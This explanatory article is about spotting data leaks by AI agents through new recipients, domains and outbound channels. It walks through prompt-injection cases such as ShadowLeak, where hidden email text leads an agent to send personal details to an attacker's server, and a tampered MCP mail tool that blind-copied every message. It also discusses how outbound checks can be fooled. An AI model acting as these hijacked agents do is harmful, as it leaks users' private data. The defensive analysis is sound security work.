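# New destinations and outbound channels as warning signs that an AI agent is leaking data

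## How does data leave an AI assistant?

Data exfiltration is the transfer of private data to someone who should not have it. An AI agent is a language model with tools that let it read a mailbox, open web pages or send messages. An outsider who manages to steer the agent can use it to exfiltrate data. The theft succeeds only if the data leaves through an outbound channel, such as an email, a web request or an image that loads automatically, and reaches a destination. Security teams therefore check outbound channels and destinations for warning signs. One obvious sign is a new destination, meaning a mailbox or web address that does not appear in a specified record, such as the user's past mail or the organisation's past traffic.

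### Prompt injection

Outsiders usually steer an agent by prompt injection. The attacker places instructions in content the model will read, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. Fortune (2025) gives the example of a web page containing instructions, invisible to human visitors, for an agent to share a user's emails or drain a bank account.

Prompt injection works because a language model has no internal boundary between instructions and data, as David C explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. The model only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far. If a recruiter's system gives the model a CV to assess, a hidden sentence in the CV can act as an instruction to approve the candidate. Programmers can prevent SQL injection, a similar weakness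 in databases, by sending commands and data separately. David C thinks it very possible that no equally complete fix for prompt injection will ever be found.

### Three conditions for theft

An attacker who hijacks an agent still needs a way to get data out. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the programmer Simon Willison (2025) writes that an attacker needs an agent that has access to private data, reads untrusted content, and can send data out. An email assistant easily meets all three conditions, since any stranger can write to the mailbox that holds the private mail. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) uses a two-part scheme from software security, in which an attacker needs a "source" (a way to influence the system) and a "sink" (a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as following a link).

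Taking away any one of the conditions stops this kind of theft, and Willison (2026) calls outward communication "by far the easiest leg to restrict" if the system is to stay useful. Access to private data is often why people connect an assistant. Untrusted content is hard to keep out because attackers have so many ways to get text in front of a model. Willison makes this point in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* about the code editor Cursor, whose makers answered one report of a leak by advising users to connect only to sources with trusted content. Outbound requests, by contrast, pass through ordinary code, which can refuse them by a fixed rule that gives the same result however the attacker words the instructions.

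His example was Lockdown Mode, a ChatGPT setting that OpenAI began to roll out to personal accounts in June 2026. It limits outbound network requests but does not remove injected instructions from what the model reads, and OpenAI warns that these can still distort an answer. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, recommended it only for people at elevated risk, because it disables some functionality.

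Past repairs support Willison's view. His 2025 essay lists 17 cases of this attack, starting with ChatGPT in April 2023, and he reports that vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the route that let data out. But there are many routes to close, because any tool that can make a web request, load an image or show the user a link can carry data out. A vendor can close the routes in its own product, but not those in a tool that the user adds from elsewhere.

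These leaks may matter less as models learn to ignore injected instructions, but some attacks may still succeed. OpenAI reports that most of the attempts it knows of to extract secrets from ChatGPT conversations fail because the model refuses. In August 2026 Anthropic published a test it had commissioned from Trajectory Labs, an outside firm, in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three of its models in the "auto mode" of its coding agent, Claude Code. Willison said he would love to believe that Anthropic had solved the problem, but wanted more independent confirmation. Even if the 720 attempts had been independent, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate of about 0.4 per cent, and they were not independent, since they came from 72 scenarios. An attacker who can try many wordings on many targets needs only one success. Fortune reported in December 2025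 that OpenAI expects some attacks on AI browsers to persist.

### What a web address carries

Many of the outbound channels come down to one event, a request for a web address. Take this harmless one:

`https://example.com/log?q=blue+umbrella`

The opening `https` selects an encrypted connection. `example.com` is the domain, which determines whose server receives the request. `/log` is the path, which identifies the page or function the visitor wants. The parameters follow the question mark. This URL has one, named `q`, with the value `blue+umbrella`, where the plus sign stands for a space. Sites routinely use parameters for ordinary purposes, such as sending search terms to a search engine.

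When a program opens the address, it looks up the network location of `example.com`, connects, and asks for `/log?q=blue+umbrella`. This is a GET request, the standard way of asking for a page. The server needs the whole text to determine what to send back. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020), a study of chat apps, explains that the server also receives the requester's IP address, the number the reply must be sent to. Web servers commonly write the requested address into a log, where the owner of `example.com` can read "blue umbrella".

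Requesting the page has therefore delivered a message without an upload. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes how attackers exploit this by getting the model to request a URL that contains private text, such as an email address or a document title, in place of the harmless phrase. The page need not exist, because a server can log the request even if it answers "not found". Encryption doesn't prevent this, because it protects the text only in transit, and whoever runs the receiving server can read it. The private text can also be in the path, as in `https://example.com/blue-umbrella`, so a filter that strips parameters would miss it.

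### Channel, destination and content

Whenever an AI assistant sends data out, a check can examine the channel, the destination and the content. The channel is how the data is sent, such as by email or by loading an image. The destination is whoever receives the data, identified by a mailbox, a domain, an exact web address or an account on a shared service. The content is what the recipient ends up with.

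An email gives the destination in the address line and the content in the body, but a web request holds both in one string. Changing `blue+umbrella` to `red+umbrella` leaves the domain the same, but the exact address may be one that nobody has requested before. Only a check that compares exact addresses, rather than domains, would then find something new. A familiar destination can also receive content it should never have had. Willison describes a demonstration in which researchers got an agent to publish the names of a developer's private projects on GitHub, a code-sharing site that developers use routinely.

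The main channels differ in who makes the request, whether a person has to act first, and whether anyone can undo the result.

| Channel | Who makes the request | Does someone have to click? | Can the sender take it back? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email | The user's mail service, on the agent's instruction | No, unless the product asks for approval | Generally not after delivery |
| Page fetch | The assistant provider's server, or the user's machine if the agent runs there | No | No |
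| Rendered image | The user's browser or app, or a server that fetches images on its behalf | No | No |
| Clicked link | The user's browser | Yes | No |
| Link preview | A messaging company's server, or the sender's or recipient's app | No | No, even if the user deletes the message |
| Webhook or other tool call | The server or machine that runs the tool | No, unless the product asks for approval | Seldom; it depends on the receiving service |
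| Post to a shared place | The server or machine that runs the tool, under the user's account | No, unless the product asks for approval | In part: the user can delete the post, but not copies that others have made |

A link preview is the title and picture that a messaging app shows under a link. To create one, a program has to open the link. Mysk found in 2020 that iMessage, Signal and WhatsApp opened it on the sender's phone, while Slack, Discord, LinkedIn and Zoom used the company's own servers. Two other apps used the recipient's phone, which opened the link as soon as the message came into view; one had fixed this by publication and the other was still working on a fix. Previews posed little risk when people wrote the links, but Willison (2024) pointed out that a hijacked chatbot can post a link containing private data, which is sent to the linked site when the preview is created. PromptArmor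 notes in *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* that without previews, the user would typically have to click the link.

Company documentation confirms which company's systems make the requests in several of these cases. OpenAI states that when a user's question leads ChatGPT to visit a page, the visit is labeled ChatGPT-User, and it publishes the IP addresses these visits come from. Slack has a page describing its robots for website owners who have found them in their access logs. One robot opens links that users post, another fetches and stores posted images, and a general-purpose one sends customer-configured outgoing webhooks, among other things.

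The last column of the table determines when a check has to run. A web request finishes in a fraction of a second, so a warning that arrives afterwards can report the loss but can't prevent it.

### Who can see the request

An employee's browser normally reaches the internet through the employer's network. If a hijacked assistant displays an image from an attacker's server, the browser's request for that image crosses the company's firewall, where a filter can compare the domain with a list or at least record it. If the assistant fetches a page from its provider's data centre, the request travels from the provider to the destination and never enters the company's network.

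In *ShadowLeak* (2025), the security firm Radware demonstrated an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research, an agent that reads web pages or a user's connected mailbox and writes a report. The attacker sends an employee an ordinary-looking email with instructions hidden in tiny or white-on-white type. When the employee later asks the agent to summarise the day's mail, the agent reads the hidden instructions, collects personal details from other messages, puts them into a web address on the attacker's server and requests that address. The employee doesn't have to click anything or open the email. Radware argues that even strict monitoring and lists of approved addresses at the employer's network boundary cannot stop the request, because it starts on OpenAI's servers. Earlier zero-click leaks relied on the user's own software to load an image, so the private data passed through something the employer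 controlled.

In Radware's tests, a simple version of the attack email worked about half the time. It worked considerably more often once the researchers added urgency and made the receiving address look like an internal compliance service. OpenAI reprints part of a 2025 attack email that appears to be the same one, and also gives a success rate of 50 per cent. The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent* quotes the researchers as saying that the email had to overcome the agent's resistance to sending personal data to an unfamiliar address. Persuasive text was enough to do this, but it would not have affected a check in ordinary code, which would not have read the email.

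Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025, OpenAI said by early August that it had fixed it, and Radware published its findings in September. A Radware spokesperson told The Record that the firm had not seen real attackers use the flaw. Customers have no network traffic to inspect, so for them such leaks are "nearly impossible to detect", in the words of Radware, which sells security products, including one for AI agents. The provider, however, makes the request and can keep a record of it. Radware recommends logging every action an agent takes, and David C advises developers to log tool use and calls to other services, including failed ones, since an attacker will probably need several tries. For page fetches, the provider therefore has to check for new destinations or give the customer a record good enough to do so.

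### Risk signals

A risk signal is an observation that turns up more often in hijacked sessions than in ordinary ones, so seeing it raises the probability that someone has hijacked the agent. It may still be common in ordinary sessions. In ShadowLeak, the request to an unfamiliar domain and the employee's personal details in the address were both risk signals. But Deep Research is meant to open pages that its user has never visited, so a rule that treated every unfamiliar domain as proof of an attack would make the product useless.

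Before ChatGPT loads an address automatically, OpenAI's system checks whether that exact address appears in an independent index of public pages. If it doesn't, OpenAI classes the address as unverified, which does not mean the site is malicious. ChatGPT then looks for another source or shows the user a warning. OpenAI also cautions that overly strict rules cause false alarms that interrupt legitimate actions, and that frequent interruptions teach people to click through warnings without thinking. The choice between blocking an action, asking about it and holding it for review therefore depends on the strength of the signal, what the agent is about to send, and how much harm a mistake would cause.

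## When does a destination count as new, and how much does that tell?

A check for new destinations searches a record of earlier contacts (the reference history) for a unit such as a domain or a single mailbox. The same action can count as new or familiar depending on which history and unit the check's builder chooses.

### Which history

The history a destination is checked against can cover the current session, one user, the whole organisation or the public web. Suppose a company lawyer asks her AI assistant to email a parts supplier that she has never written to but that the purchasing department emails every week. A check against her own history would flag this routine message. Using the company's history would avoid that false alarm, but it would also let a hijacked assistant send her case files to the same supplier.

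Whether a destination counts as new depends on the history it is compared with. The widest history is the public web. With an index of public pages like OpenAI's, an address can count as known even if nobody at the company has ever opened it. The narrowest history is the current session, where every destination is new at the start.

Whether a destination counts as new also depends on how far back the history goes. Akamai, whose servers handle more than 80 million name lookups a second, counts a domain as newly observed if nobody in its data has looked it up in the last 60 days, according to Tilborghs and Ferreira's *Flagging 13 Million Malicious Domains in 1 Month with Newly Observed Domains* (2022). They report that other organisations use windows of between 30 minutes and 72 hours. A domain last looked up a month ago would count as new under a 72-hour window but not under Akamai's.

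Some security products look at a domain's age since registration. In *Strategically Aged Domain Detection*, the security firm Palo Alto Networks advises customers to block domains for 32 days after registration. That rule does not block a twenty-year-old website, even if it is new to the company because no employee has ever visited it.

### Which unit

In the address `notes.example.com/july`, the domain is `example.com` and the host is `notes.example.com`, the full name that a browser looks up. Hosting services often give each customer a separate host under one shared domain. *Detecting Credential Spearphishing Attacks in Enterprise Settings* (Ho, Sharma and colleagues, 2017) gives the example of `attacker.blogspot.com`. `blogspot.com` is popular and would be in most companies' histories, but the attacker's host would be new.

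For this reason, Ho and colleagues compared hosts when they built a detector for targeted phishing at Lawrence Berkeley National Laboratory, a large US research centre. They also rejected exact web addresses, because more than half of those that staff clicked in emails had never appeared in the lab's traffic before.

The SolarWinds attack, in which intruders hid a malicious program in a software company's updates, shows that whether a destination counts as new can depend on whether domains or host names are compared. According to Palo Alto Networks, the program contacted one domain but kept generating new host names under it, with the victim's identity encoded in the name. After the first contact, only a comparison of host names would have kept finding new destinations. Looking up the name was enough to send the data out, before any page was requested. But legitimate services also generate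 host names automatically, and Palo Alto Networks had to add filters to recognise them.

On a shared service, different recipients can share a host, so the check has to compare email addresses or accounts. A stranger's Gmail address has the same domain as a colleague's private one, and a stranger's GitHub project is on the same host as the company's own.

### From a new destination to a probability

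Bayes' rule gives the probability that an action is a hijack once a check has found its destination to be new. Let H mean that a hijacked agent is acting for the attacker, and N that the destination is new:

`P(H given N) = P(N given H) × P(H) / [P(N given H) × P(H) + P(N given not H) × P(not H)]`

P(H) is the base rate, the share of all outbound actions that are hijacks. In this illustration, it is 1 in 100,000, and 95 per cent of hijacks and 10 per cent of legitimate actions go to a new destination. These are round figures, not measurements. The table applies them to ten million actions. Its last two rows add a second sign, which the first result does not depend on.

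| Actions | Hijacks | Legitimate | Share that are hijacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| All | 100 | 9,999,900 | 1 in 100,000 |
| To a familiar destination | 5 | 8,999,910 | 1 in 1.8 million |
| To a new destination | 95 | 999,990 | about 1 in 10,500 |
| New destination and second sign, independent | 85.5 | 1,000 | about 1 in 13 (8 per cent) |
| New destination and second sign, fully overlapping in legitimate actions | 85.5 | 10,000 | about 1 in 118 (0.8 per cent) |

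About one in 10,500 alerts on a new destination is a real hijack. A new destination is 9.5 times as common in hijacks as in legitimate actions, so seeing one makes a hijack about 9.5 times as likely, but hijacks are very rare to begin with. Still, under these assumptions, 95 per cent of hijacks are in the tenth of traffic that gets flagged, so a slower or more expensive check could run on that tenth alone.

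Now suppose the check also looks for text copied from the user's private mail, which appears in 90 per cent of hijacks and 0.1 per cent of legitimate actions. If the two signs are independent within each group, private text is equally likely whether the destination is new or familiar. Both signs then appear together in 85.5 hijacks and about 1,000 legitimate actions, so the probability of a hijack rises to about 8 per cent. Most of the rise comes from the private text, which would give 0.9 per cent by itself.

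The two signs may well not be independent among legitimate actions. People often give a site personal details because they are using it for the first time, for example when they ask an agent to register them for a conference or book a hotel. In the extreme case, every legitimate action that contains private text goes to a new destination. Both signs then appear in 10,000 legitimate actions, and the probability of a hijack falls back to about 0.8 per cent, so the new destination adds no evidence beyond the private text. Dependence among the hijacks matters much less, because both signs must appear together in between 85 and 90 of every 100 hijacks.

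A check could also raise the base rate by examining only actions that follow untrusted content, because an agent that has read nothing from outsiders cannot have picked up a prompt injection. If 1 in 1,000 of those actions were hijacks and the other assumptions held, two independent signs would make a hijack about 90 per cent likely.

### The base-rate problem

Security researchers encountered this problem long before AI agents existed. Stefan Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) applied Bayes' rule to software that monitors computers for break-ins. His example was a small installation with two intrusions and a million log records a day, which he grouped into 100,000 events.

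The share of a detector's alarms that are correct depends far more on its false-alarm rate than on its detection rate. If a detector catches every intrusion and raises false alarms on about 1 in 100,000 events, two-thirds of its alarms are correct. If it catches only 70 per cent of intrusions, that share drops to about 58 per cent. But if the false-alarm rate rises to 1 in 1,000, only about 2 per cent of alarms are correct, even when the detector catches every intrusion.

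Axelsson then compared this requirement with published tests. The detectors that flagged unusual behaviour raised false alarms at least ten times too often, while some that looked for signs of known attacks came close to meeting the requirement. The test results are decades old, but the arithmetic still applies to any rare event. A check for new destinations is a detector of unusual behaviour, and its assumed false-alarm rate of 10 per cent is 10,000 times the rate Axelsson required.

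*Intrusion-Detection Policies for IT Security Breaches* explains that defenders waste resources if they act on every signal, because most are false, but that the detector is useless if they ignore the signals.

### Evidence from company mail and web traffic

Ho and colleagues worked with an even lower base rate, fewer than ten known cases of targeted phishing in about 370 million emails. In the theft they wanted to stop, an employee follows a link and types a password into the attacker's site, which resembles a leak by an agent.

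If the lab had raised an alert for every sender name it had never seen before, it would have had over 1.1 million alerts in nearly four years, even excluding senders who later became regular correspondents. The false-alarm rate would have been only about 0.3 per cent, but that is nearly 800 alerts a day, and the researchers were aiming for ten a day. Security staff sampled these emails and found conference invitations, mailing-list notices, advertisements for trial software and messages from help desks.

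The researchers therefore combined four measures. For each click on a link in an email, their detector counted earlier visits by anyone at the lab to the same host, and the days between the first such visit and the email's arrival. The other two measures concerned the sender, and one of them was the number of earlier days on which the same name and address had appeared together. A click's score was the number of other clicks that were no more suspicious than it on any of the four measures, so a click that was odd in only one respect scored low.

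Limited to ten alerts a day, the detector caught 17 of 19 attacks at a false-alarm rate of 0.004 per cent. Kernel density estimation, a standard statistical method, needed 91 alerts a day to catch as many from the same measures, partly because it also flagged events that were rare in a harmless way. Even the detector's alerts were nearly all false, since ten a day over the 1,232-day test comes to about 12,000 alerts for 17 attacks.

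The method applies to agents more readily than the numbers do. Ho and colleagues measured people clicking links in email, and an agent that opens pages by itself may reach new hosts much more often. Their main detector also raised its alert after the click, which would be too late if the agent's request already contained the data. They considered showing a warning page before a suspicious link opened, and calculated that the median employee would have seen two of these pages in nearly four years.

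A hijacked agent is perhaps closer to a hijacked employee account, because both send from an address that recipients already trust. *Detecting and Characterizing Lateral Phishing at Scale (2019)* presents a classifier that detects phishing from such accounts, with fewer than four false alarms per million emails sent by employees. If a check on agents had four false alarms per million and still caught 95 per cent of hijacks, about 70 per cent of its alerts would be right at the assumed base rate of 1 in 100,000. A new destination alone, at 10 per cent, is far from that.

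*Detection of Early-Stage Enterprise Infection by Mining Large-Scale Log Data (2014)* uses new destinations only to narrow the search. It analyses 38 terabytes of web traffic collected over two months at a large company. The method keeps only rare destinations, including domains that no machine in the company had previously visited within the observation window. It then starts from machines or domains already under suspicion and follows their connections to find others that are probably part of the same attack. This found hundreds of suspicious domains that the company's security products had missed. For an agent, the equivalent would be to treat a new destination as a reason to examine the rest of the session.

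### How many new domains are malicious?

Security firms that watch domain lookups across many networks report very different shares, largely because they mean different things by "new" and by "malicious".

| Source | What counts as new | Share and what it measures |
|---|---|---|
| Palo Alto Networks | Newly registered | 1.27 per cent malicious |
| Dark Reading | In the first seven days of life | 6.7 per cent put on a blocklist |
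| Tilborghs and Ferreira | No lookup in 60 days | 20.1 per cent flagged as malicious |
| Infoblox | Newly observed in the past year | 22.5 per cent malicious or suspicious |

The second row comes from *The modality of mortality in domain names (2019)*, a study of 23.8 million domains that started from the popular claim that most new domains are malicious. Dark Reading's *'Short, Brutal Lives'* reports that 9.3 per cent of the domains died within a week, mostly through blocklisting. That figure gives the claim little support, although a week is too short to catch domains that turn malicious later. The last row's figure, 27 million out of 120 million domains, comes from Infoblox's *2026 Threat Landscape Report*.

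The higher figures come from companies that sell protection against such domains, and outsiders can do little to check them. Tilborghs and Ferreira found only 329 false positives among almost 79 million flagged domains, but they relied partly on customers to report errors. A large outside database had assessments for about 1 in 11,000 of the domains they flagged.

A fifth of new domains may be malicious, but that figure can't be used as the share of an agent's requests to new destinations that are hijacks. Attackers register domains in bulk, and many of these get little traffic, so malicious domains make up a larger share of domains than of visits. Most also serve phishing or malware rather than collecting data from an agent. Akamai's domains are new to everyone in a very large body of traffic, which is much rarer than being new to one user. Checking destinations against a history drawn from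 many users therefore gives fewer false alarms, but it misses an attacker whose domain someone else has already looked up.

How often that happens depends partly on how old malicious domains are. *A Longitudinal Study of Recently Observed Malicious Domains* (Mashood and Nabeel, 2026) covers 1.52 million domains that at least five scanning engines had flagged, all first seen between January and May 2026. Among those that attackers had apparently created, 7.4 per cent were a day old or less at first detection and 29.9 per cent were a week old or less. The median age was 60 days, so a rule that blocks domains for their first 32 days would no longer have applied to more than half of them at first detection.

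The true ages may be higher still, because the study classed every domain at least three years old as a compromised legitimate site and so left any old domains that attackers owned out of the calculation. Compromised sites made up 10.7 per cent of the collection, and a test of registration age would miss nearly all of them.

A first-contact test, which checks a destination against the organisation's own history, works better here because an old domain can still be new to the organisation. Infoblox's *The Cybercrime Machine* (2026) reports that 88 per cent of threat-related domains appeared in only one customer's network and that 44 per cent were active for a single day. Lists of domains already detected elsewhere would often come too late to catch these.

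### New users, research agents and patient attackers

Every destination is new for a user with no history, so newness can't distinguish hijacks from legitimate actions. Ho and colleagues measured how much history their detector needed. With three months of records, it caught the same attacks as with six, at the same median of seven alerts a day. With one month, it missed an attack and the median rose to 18. An assistant that connects to an established mailbox can start with years of sent mail, and an employer can provide the organisation's history for a new employee. A new private user has neither, so a check would have to rely on the public web or other signs until a history builds up.

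A research agent such as Deep Research always faces the same difficulty. If 80 per cent of its legitimate requests went to new destinations, and the other assumptions stayed the same, about one alert in 84,000 would be right, barely better than picking a request at random. More history for the same user would not help much. Checking addresses against the public web might, because the pages a research agent needs are mostly public, while an address that an attacker has filled with private text usually is not.

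An attacker can also make a destination familiar before using it. Axelsson lists this as a weakness of detectors that learn what is normal, since an intruder can gradually teach them to accept his activity. Ho and colleagues describe a phisher who sends harmless emails for several days to build up a record, though each one increases the risk that somebody notices the false name. An attacker targeting an email assistant could ask an innocent question and wait for the reply, which would put his address in the user's sent mail. An attacker targeting a research agent could publish a useful page and let the agent visit it in a session before the attack.

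The SolarWinds attackers registered their domain in 2018, about two years before heavy traffic to it began. Palo Alto Networks reports that the malicious program contacted it occasionally before then, with little traffic. When the main attack started, the domain was therefore no longer newly registered or new to the victims' networks. The firm now looks for domains that stay quiet for months and then receive a burst of traffic. It classed 3.8 per cent of these as malicious, three times the share among newly registered domains.

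Attackers can avoid the wait by using a site that is already familiar. One of the two attacks that Ho and colleagues missed used a page on Dropbox, a file-sharing service whose host had a good reputation at the lab. The lab's monitor also could not read encrypted connections, so it could not see the individual page.

If only the user's own actions can add a destination to the history, an attacker cannot make a site familiar by getting the agent to visit it first. The check can also record the date and type of each contact, so that one reply to a stranger last week counts for less than years of correspondence, and a site the agent has only read from does not become an approved place to send data.

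## When is a first-time email recipient a warning sign?

A first-time recipient is a strong warning sign when the agent found the address in something it read, but a weak one when the user typed it. A check can often distinguish these cases, because emails list their recipients and most mailboxes contain years of correspondence to compare them with.

### How a recipient check works

Ordinary code can run the check after the agent has drafted a message and before the mail service sends it:

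1. Collect every address in the "to", copy and blind-copy fields. Blind copies need particular care because the other recipients cannot see them.
2. Normalise each address, so that two spellings of one mailbox match. This means converting capitals to lower case and ignoring the display name, since anyone can call an account "Dana Reyes".
3. Look the address up in the user's sent mail and contact list.
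4. Find out where the agent got the address: from the user's words, from the contact list, or from text it read, such as an email or a web page.

Normalising an address too far can make a forged address match a real one. Some letters in other alphabets look the same as Latin letters, and code that converts them to Latin before the lookup would accept the forgery, so the lookup should use the exact characters. Mailing lists are a separate problem, because one familiar address may deliver to people the user has never written to.

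A simple way to find where the address came from is to search for it in the user's request, then the contact list, then everything the agent has read during the session. If it appears in none of these, the model may have made it up, which is also a reason to stop.

### Four versions of one task

Suppose a user asks her assistant to "send the quarterly report to Dana". The result depends on which address the agent uses.

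| Address | Check for newness alone | Check that also traces the origin |
|---|---|---|
| Dana's usual address, from the contact list | Passes | Passes |
| A new address that the user typed | Flags | Passes |
| A new address from an incoming message | Flags | Flags |
| A lookalike of Dana's usual address | Flags | Flags, unless the user pasted it in herself |

A check based only on whether a recipient is new would flag an address the user has just typed in her request, and the warning would only repeat her own instruction. The check would also miss an attack in which a hidden instruction tells the agent to copy the report to a former contractor. If the contractor is in the user's sent mail, the address isn't new, even though the user never mentioned the contractor.

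*Agent-Sentry* (2026) gives an example in which the new address comes from an incoming email. A user asks an agent to find a colleague's notes on a project and forward them to a second colleague, Julie Martinez. One of the emails the agent retrieves contains a request to send the whole thread to a different address because the sender's own is supposedly down. The paper treats this as an attack because the address appears only in that email and the user had named someone else.

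Sometimes the incoming message is genuine, for example if Dana changed jobs and wrote from her new account. The origin of the address isn't enough to tell her message from a forgery, but the user could check by phoning her.

She might also have told the agent to use the address in Dana's last email, in which case she approved the source without seeing the address. *Environment Steering* (2026) has a two-part rule for requests like this. The address must appear in the source the task depends on, and a judge then checks that source for signs that a prompt injection planted the address. Code can apply the first part exactly, but the judge has to interpret text and can make mistakes.

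When an agent replies to an email, it takes the recipient from the incoming message. If the user asked for the reply, she chose that recipient. But an attacker's email can also tell the agent to reply with private data, so the check has to establish whether the user asked for a reply.

A lookalike address imitates a known one, as `dana@examp1e.com` does by using the digit 1 in place of the letter l. A newness check would flag it, but if the warning only displayed the address, the user might well read it as Dana's and approve it. The check can prevent this by counting the characters that differ between each new address and the known ones, and pointing out any near match. This comparison also helps if the user copied the address from a forged invoice into her request, because a check of where the address came from would attribute it to her and let it through.

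### What research on misdirected email found

In *Preventing Information Leaks in Email*, Carvalho and Cohen (2007) tried to predict which recipient of a message the sender had added by mistake. A US regulator had made emails from the energy company Enron public, and they used those of 20 employees. They treated the oldest 90 per cent of each employee's sent mail as history and tested their predictions on the newest 10 per cent.

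The researchers added one wrong recipient to each test message to imitate an email program completing a half-typed address incorrectly. The wrong recipient came from the employee's address book and, where possible, had an address beginning with the same three characters as a real recipient's. This produced more than 1,100 simulated mistakes.

Picking a recipient at random found the mistake 40.6 per cent of the time. Comparing the text with earlier messages to each recipient raised this to about 56 per cent. Most of the improvement came from adding how often the employee had written to and heard from each person, which raised the figure to 80.4 per cent. Two further measures, one of them how often the recipients had appeared together on earlier messages, raised it to 81.4 per cent.

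Carvalho and Cohen then looked for real mistakes by searching the mail for words such as "sorry" and "mistake". They found two they could use, and the method failed on both in all 100 attempts. Neither wrong recipient had appeared in the employee's earlier mail, whereas every simulated mistake used in training had come from the address book. When the researchers retrained the method with a fifth of the simulated mistakes drawn from unseen addresses, it found one of the real mistakes about 89 per cent of the time, but its average on the simulated mistakes fell from 81.4 to 76 per cent.

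The other real message had 44 recipients, four of them new. Even though this message was known to contain a mistake, only one of the four new addresses was wrong. Past mail gave no way to tell which one, so the method was right 25 per cent of the time.

These results don't measure how many false alarms such a check would raise, because every test message contained a mistake. Carvalho and Cohen acknowledge this and suggest user studies of how many false warnings people will tolerate. Their method ranks the recipients of one message against each other, so it doesn't help when a hijacked agent writes to a single address.

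Their address book included everyone who had ever written to the employee, so an attacker could have become a known contact by sending one email. A check against hijacking should treat people as known contacts only if the user has written to them or added them to her contacts.

*Analyzing group E-mail exchange to detect data leakage* presents a method to reduce false alarms within an organisation. The method groups people by the topics of their mail and approves a recipient if the new message fits a topic that the sender and recipient share, even if they have never written to each other. This could prevent a warning when a user first writes to someone on the same project. It would help less with outsiders, because the organisation sees little of their mail.

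### Tracking an address through the agent's work

Searching earlier text for an address may fail if the model assembled it from pieces, such as a name from one message and a domain from another. CaMeL, a system Google DeepMind presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), instead records where each value came from while the agent works.

In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) describes how CaMeL handles a request to find Bob's address in the last email and send him a reminder. One model sees only the user's request and writes a short program to fetch the email, extract the address and send the reminder. A second model, which has no tools, reads the email and extracts the address. The software running the program marks the address as untrusted because it came from the email.

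CaMeL requires email recipients to be trusted. If the address it extracts is already trusted under the user's policies, it sends the email without asking the user. If the address is unknown, it can ask the user to approve the message.

Willison proposed the two-model design in 2023, without this tracking, and the CaMeL paper identified a flaw in it. Instructions hidden in the email can't change the program, because the model that writes the program never receives the email. But they can make the second model return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The program then runs as planned and sends the message to the attacker, unless a rule checks the recipient.

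The paper claims that CaMeL "effectively solves" AgentDojo, a collection of simulated tasks for testing agents against prompt injection. It also says that prompt injection is not fully solved, because users have to write and maintain the policies and may tire of approval requests.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, an agent built at Microsoft that labels data as trusted or untrusted. Once untrusted text enters the main model's context, the rules can forbid actions such as emailing an external address. Applied strictly, such a rule would stop the assistant from sending the report to a new outside address that the user had typed, because the assistant had read a stranger's email first. FIDES reduces this problem by storing untrusted text in variables, which the main model can pass to a tool without reading.

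With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo. With the rules enforced, it completed 8 per cent more tasks on average than a basic agent when using GPT-4o, and 16 per cent more when using OpenAI's o1. With the rules switched off, its extra machinery reduced task completion by 6.3 per cent compared with the basic agent. These figures don't measure how much the rules themselves reduce task completion, which would require comparing FIDES with the rules on and off. Both models date from 2024, so newer ones may lose fewer tasks.

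A trusted recipient can still be the wrong person for a particular document. Costa and colleagues' labels can therefore also list who may read each piece of data. When the agent combines data, only people on every list may receive the result. If Dana and Omar may read the quarterly report, and Dana and Priya may read the meeting notes, an email that draws on both may go only to Dana:

`{Dana, Omar} ∩ {Dana, Priya} = {Dana}`

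*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) applies both kinds of rule to AgentDojo's banking tasks. One rule requires that the recipient be trusted and be allowed to read the amount, subject and date. Its policies are slightly less strict than CaMeL's.

*Contextual Agent Security* (2025) uses a model to write a policy for each task, based on information the developers trust, such as the user's list of addresses. In one example, the policy allows email only to people on the user's work list, and only with "urgent" in the subject. Ordinary code then checks each proposed email against the policy and, if it refuses one, returns the reason to the agent. The policy can be wrong if the model misunderstands the task.

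### Forwarding rules, invitations and shared documents

Several other actions also send data to an address, so the same check can cover them.

A forwarding rule makes the mail server send copies of future messages to another address. Because the server sends these copies, a check that examined only the agent's own emails would miss them. The check therefore has to test the address whenever the agent creates or changes the rule. The standard should be stricter than for a single email, because the user can't know what the forwarded messages will contain. A new address found in an incoming message would be a particularly bad sign.

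A calendar invitation delivers its title, description and any attachments to everyone invited. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) lists calendar invitations among the ways an agent could leak data. Under a rule in *Environment Steering*, the agent may add a participant only if the address appears in an email requesting the meeting and was not planted there by an injection. The check also has to run when the agent edits an existing event, since the agent could add private text to a meeting that an outsider is already attending.

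Sharing a document gives the recipient access to the file and often to later changes. An agent can also create a link that opens the document for anyone who has it, so there is no recipient to look up. The check should treat such a link as a new destination, even if the agent sends it to a familiar person. *Environment Steering* also covers invitations to collaborate on a GitHub project, where the invited address must appear in a request email in the user's inbox.

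### A blind copy added by the tool

In September 2025, a tool called postmark-mcp leaked email to a recipient that neither the user nor the assistant had chosen. The tool was an MCP server, a program that connects an assistant to an outside service through a standard called the Model Context Protocol, and it let assistants send mail through Postmark, a commercial email service. The security firm Koi found that a developer had copied Postmark's own code and, without Postmark's involvement, published it under the same name on npm, a public library of JavaScript packages. Fifteen versions worked properly, but version 1.0.16 contained an extra line that blind-copied every email to an address of the developer's.

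The assistant would have passed the tool only the addresses that the user wanted. The tool added the blind copy afterwards, so a check on the assistant's request would have found nothing wrong. A check has to examine the final list of recipients to catch this, either as the message leaves the tool or at the service that sends it. The blind-copied address would have been new to almost every user, and it would not have come from the user's words, the contact list or anything the assistant had read.

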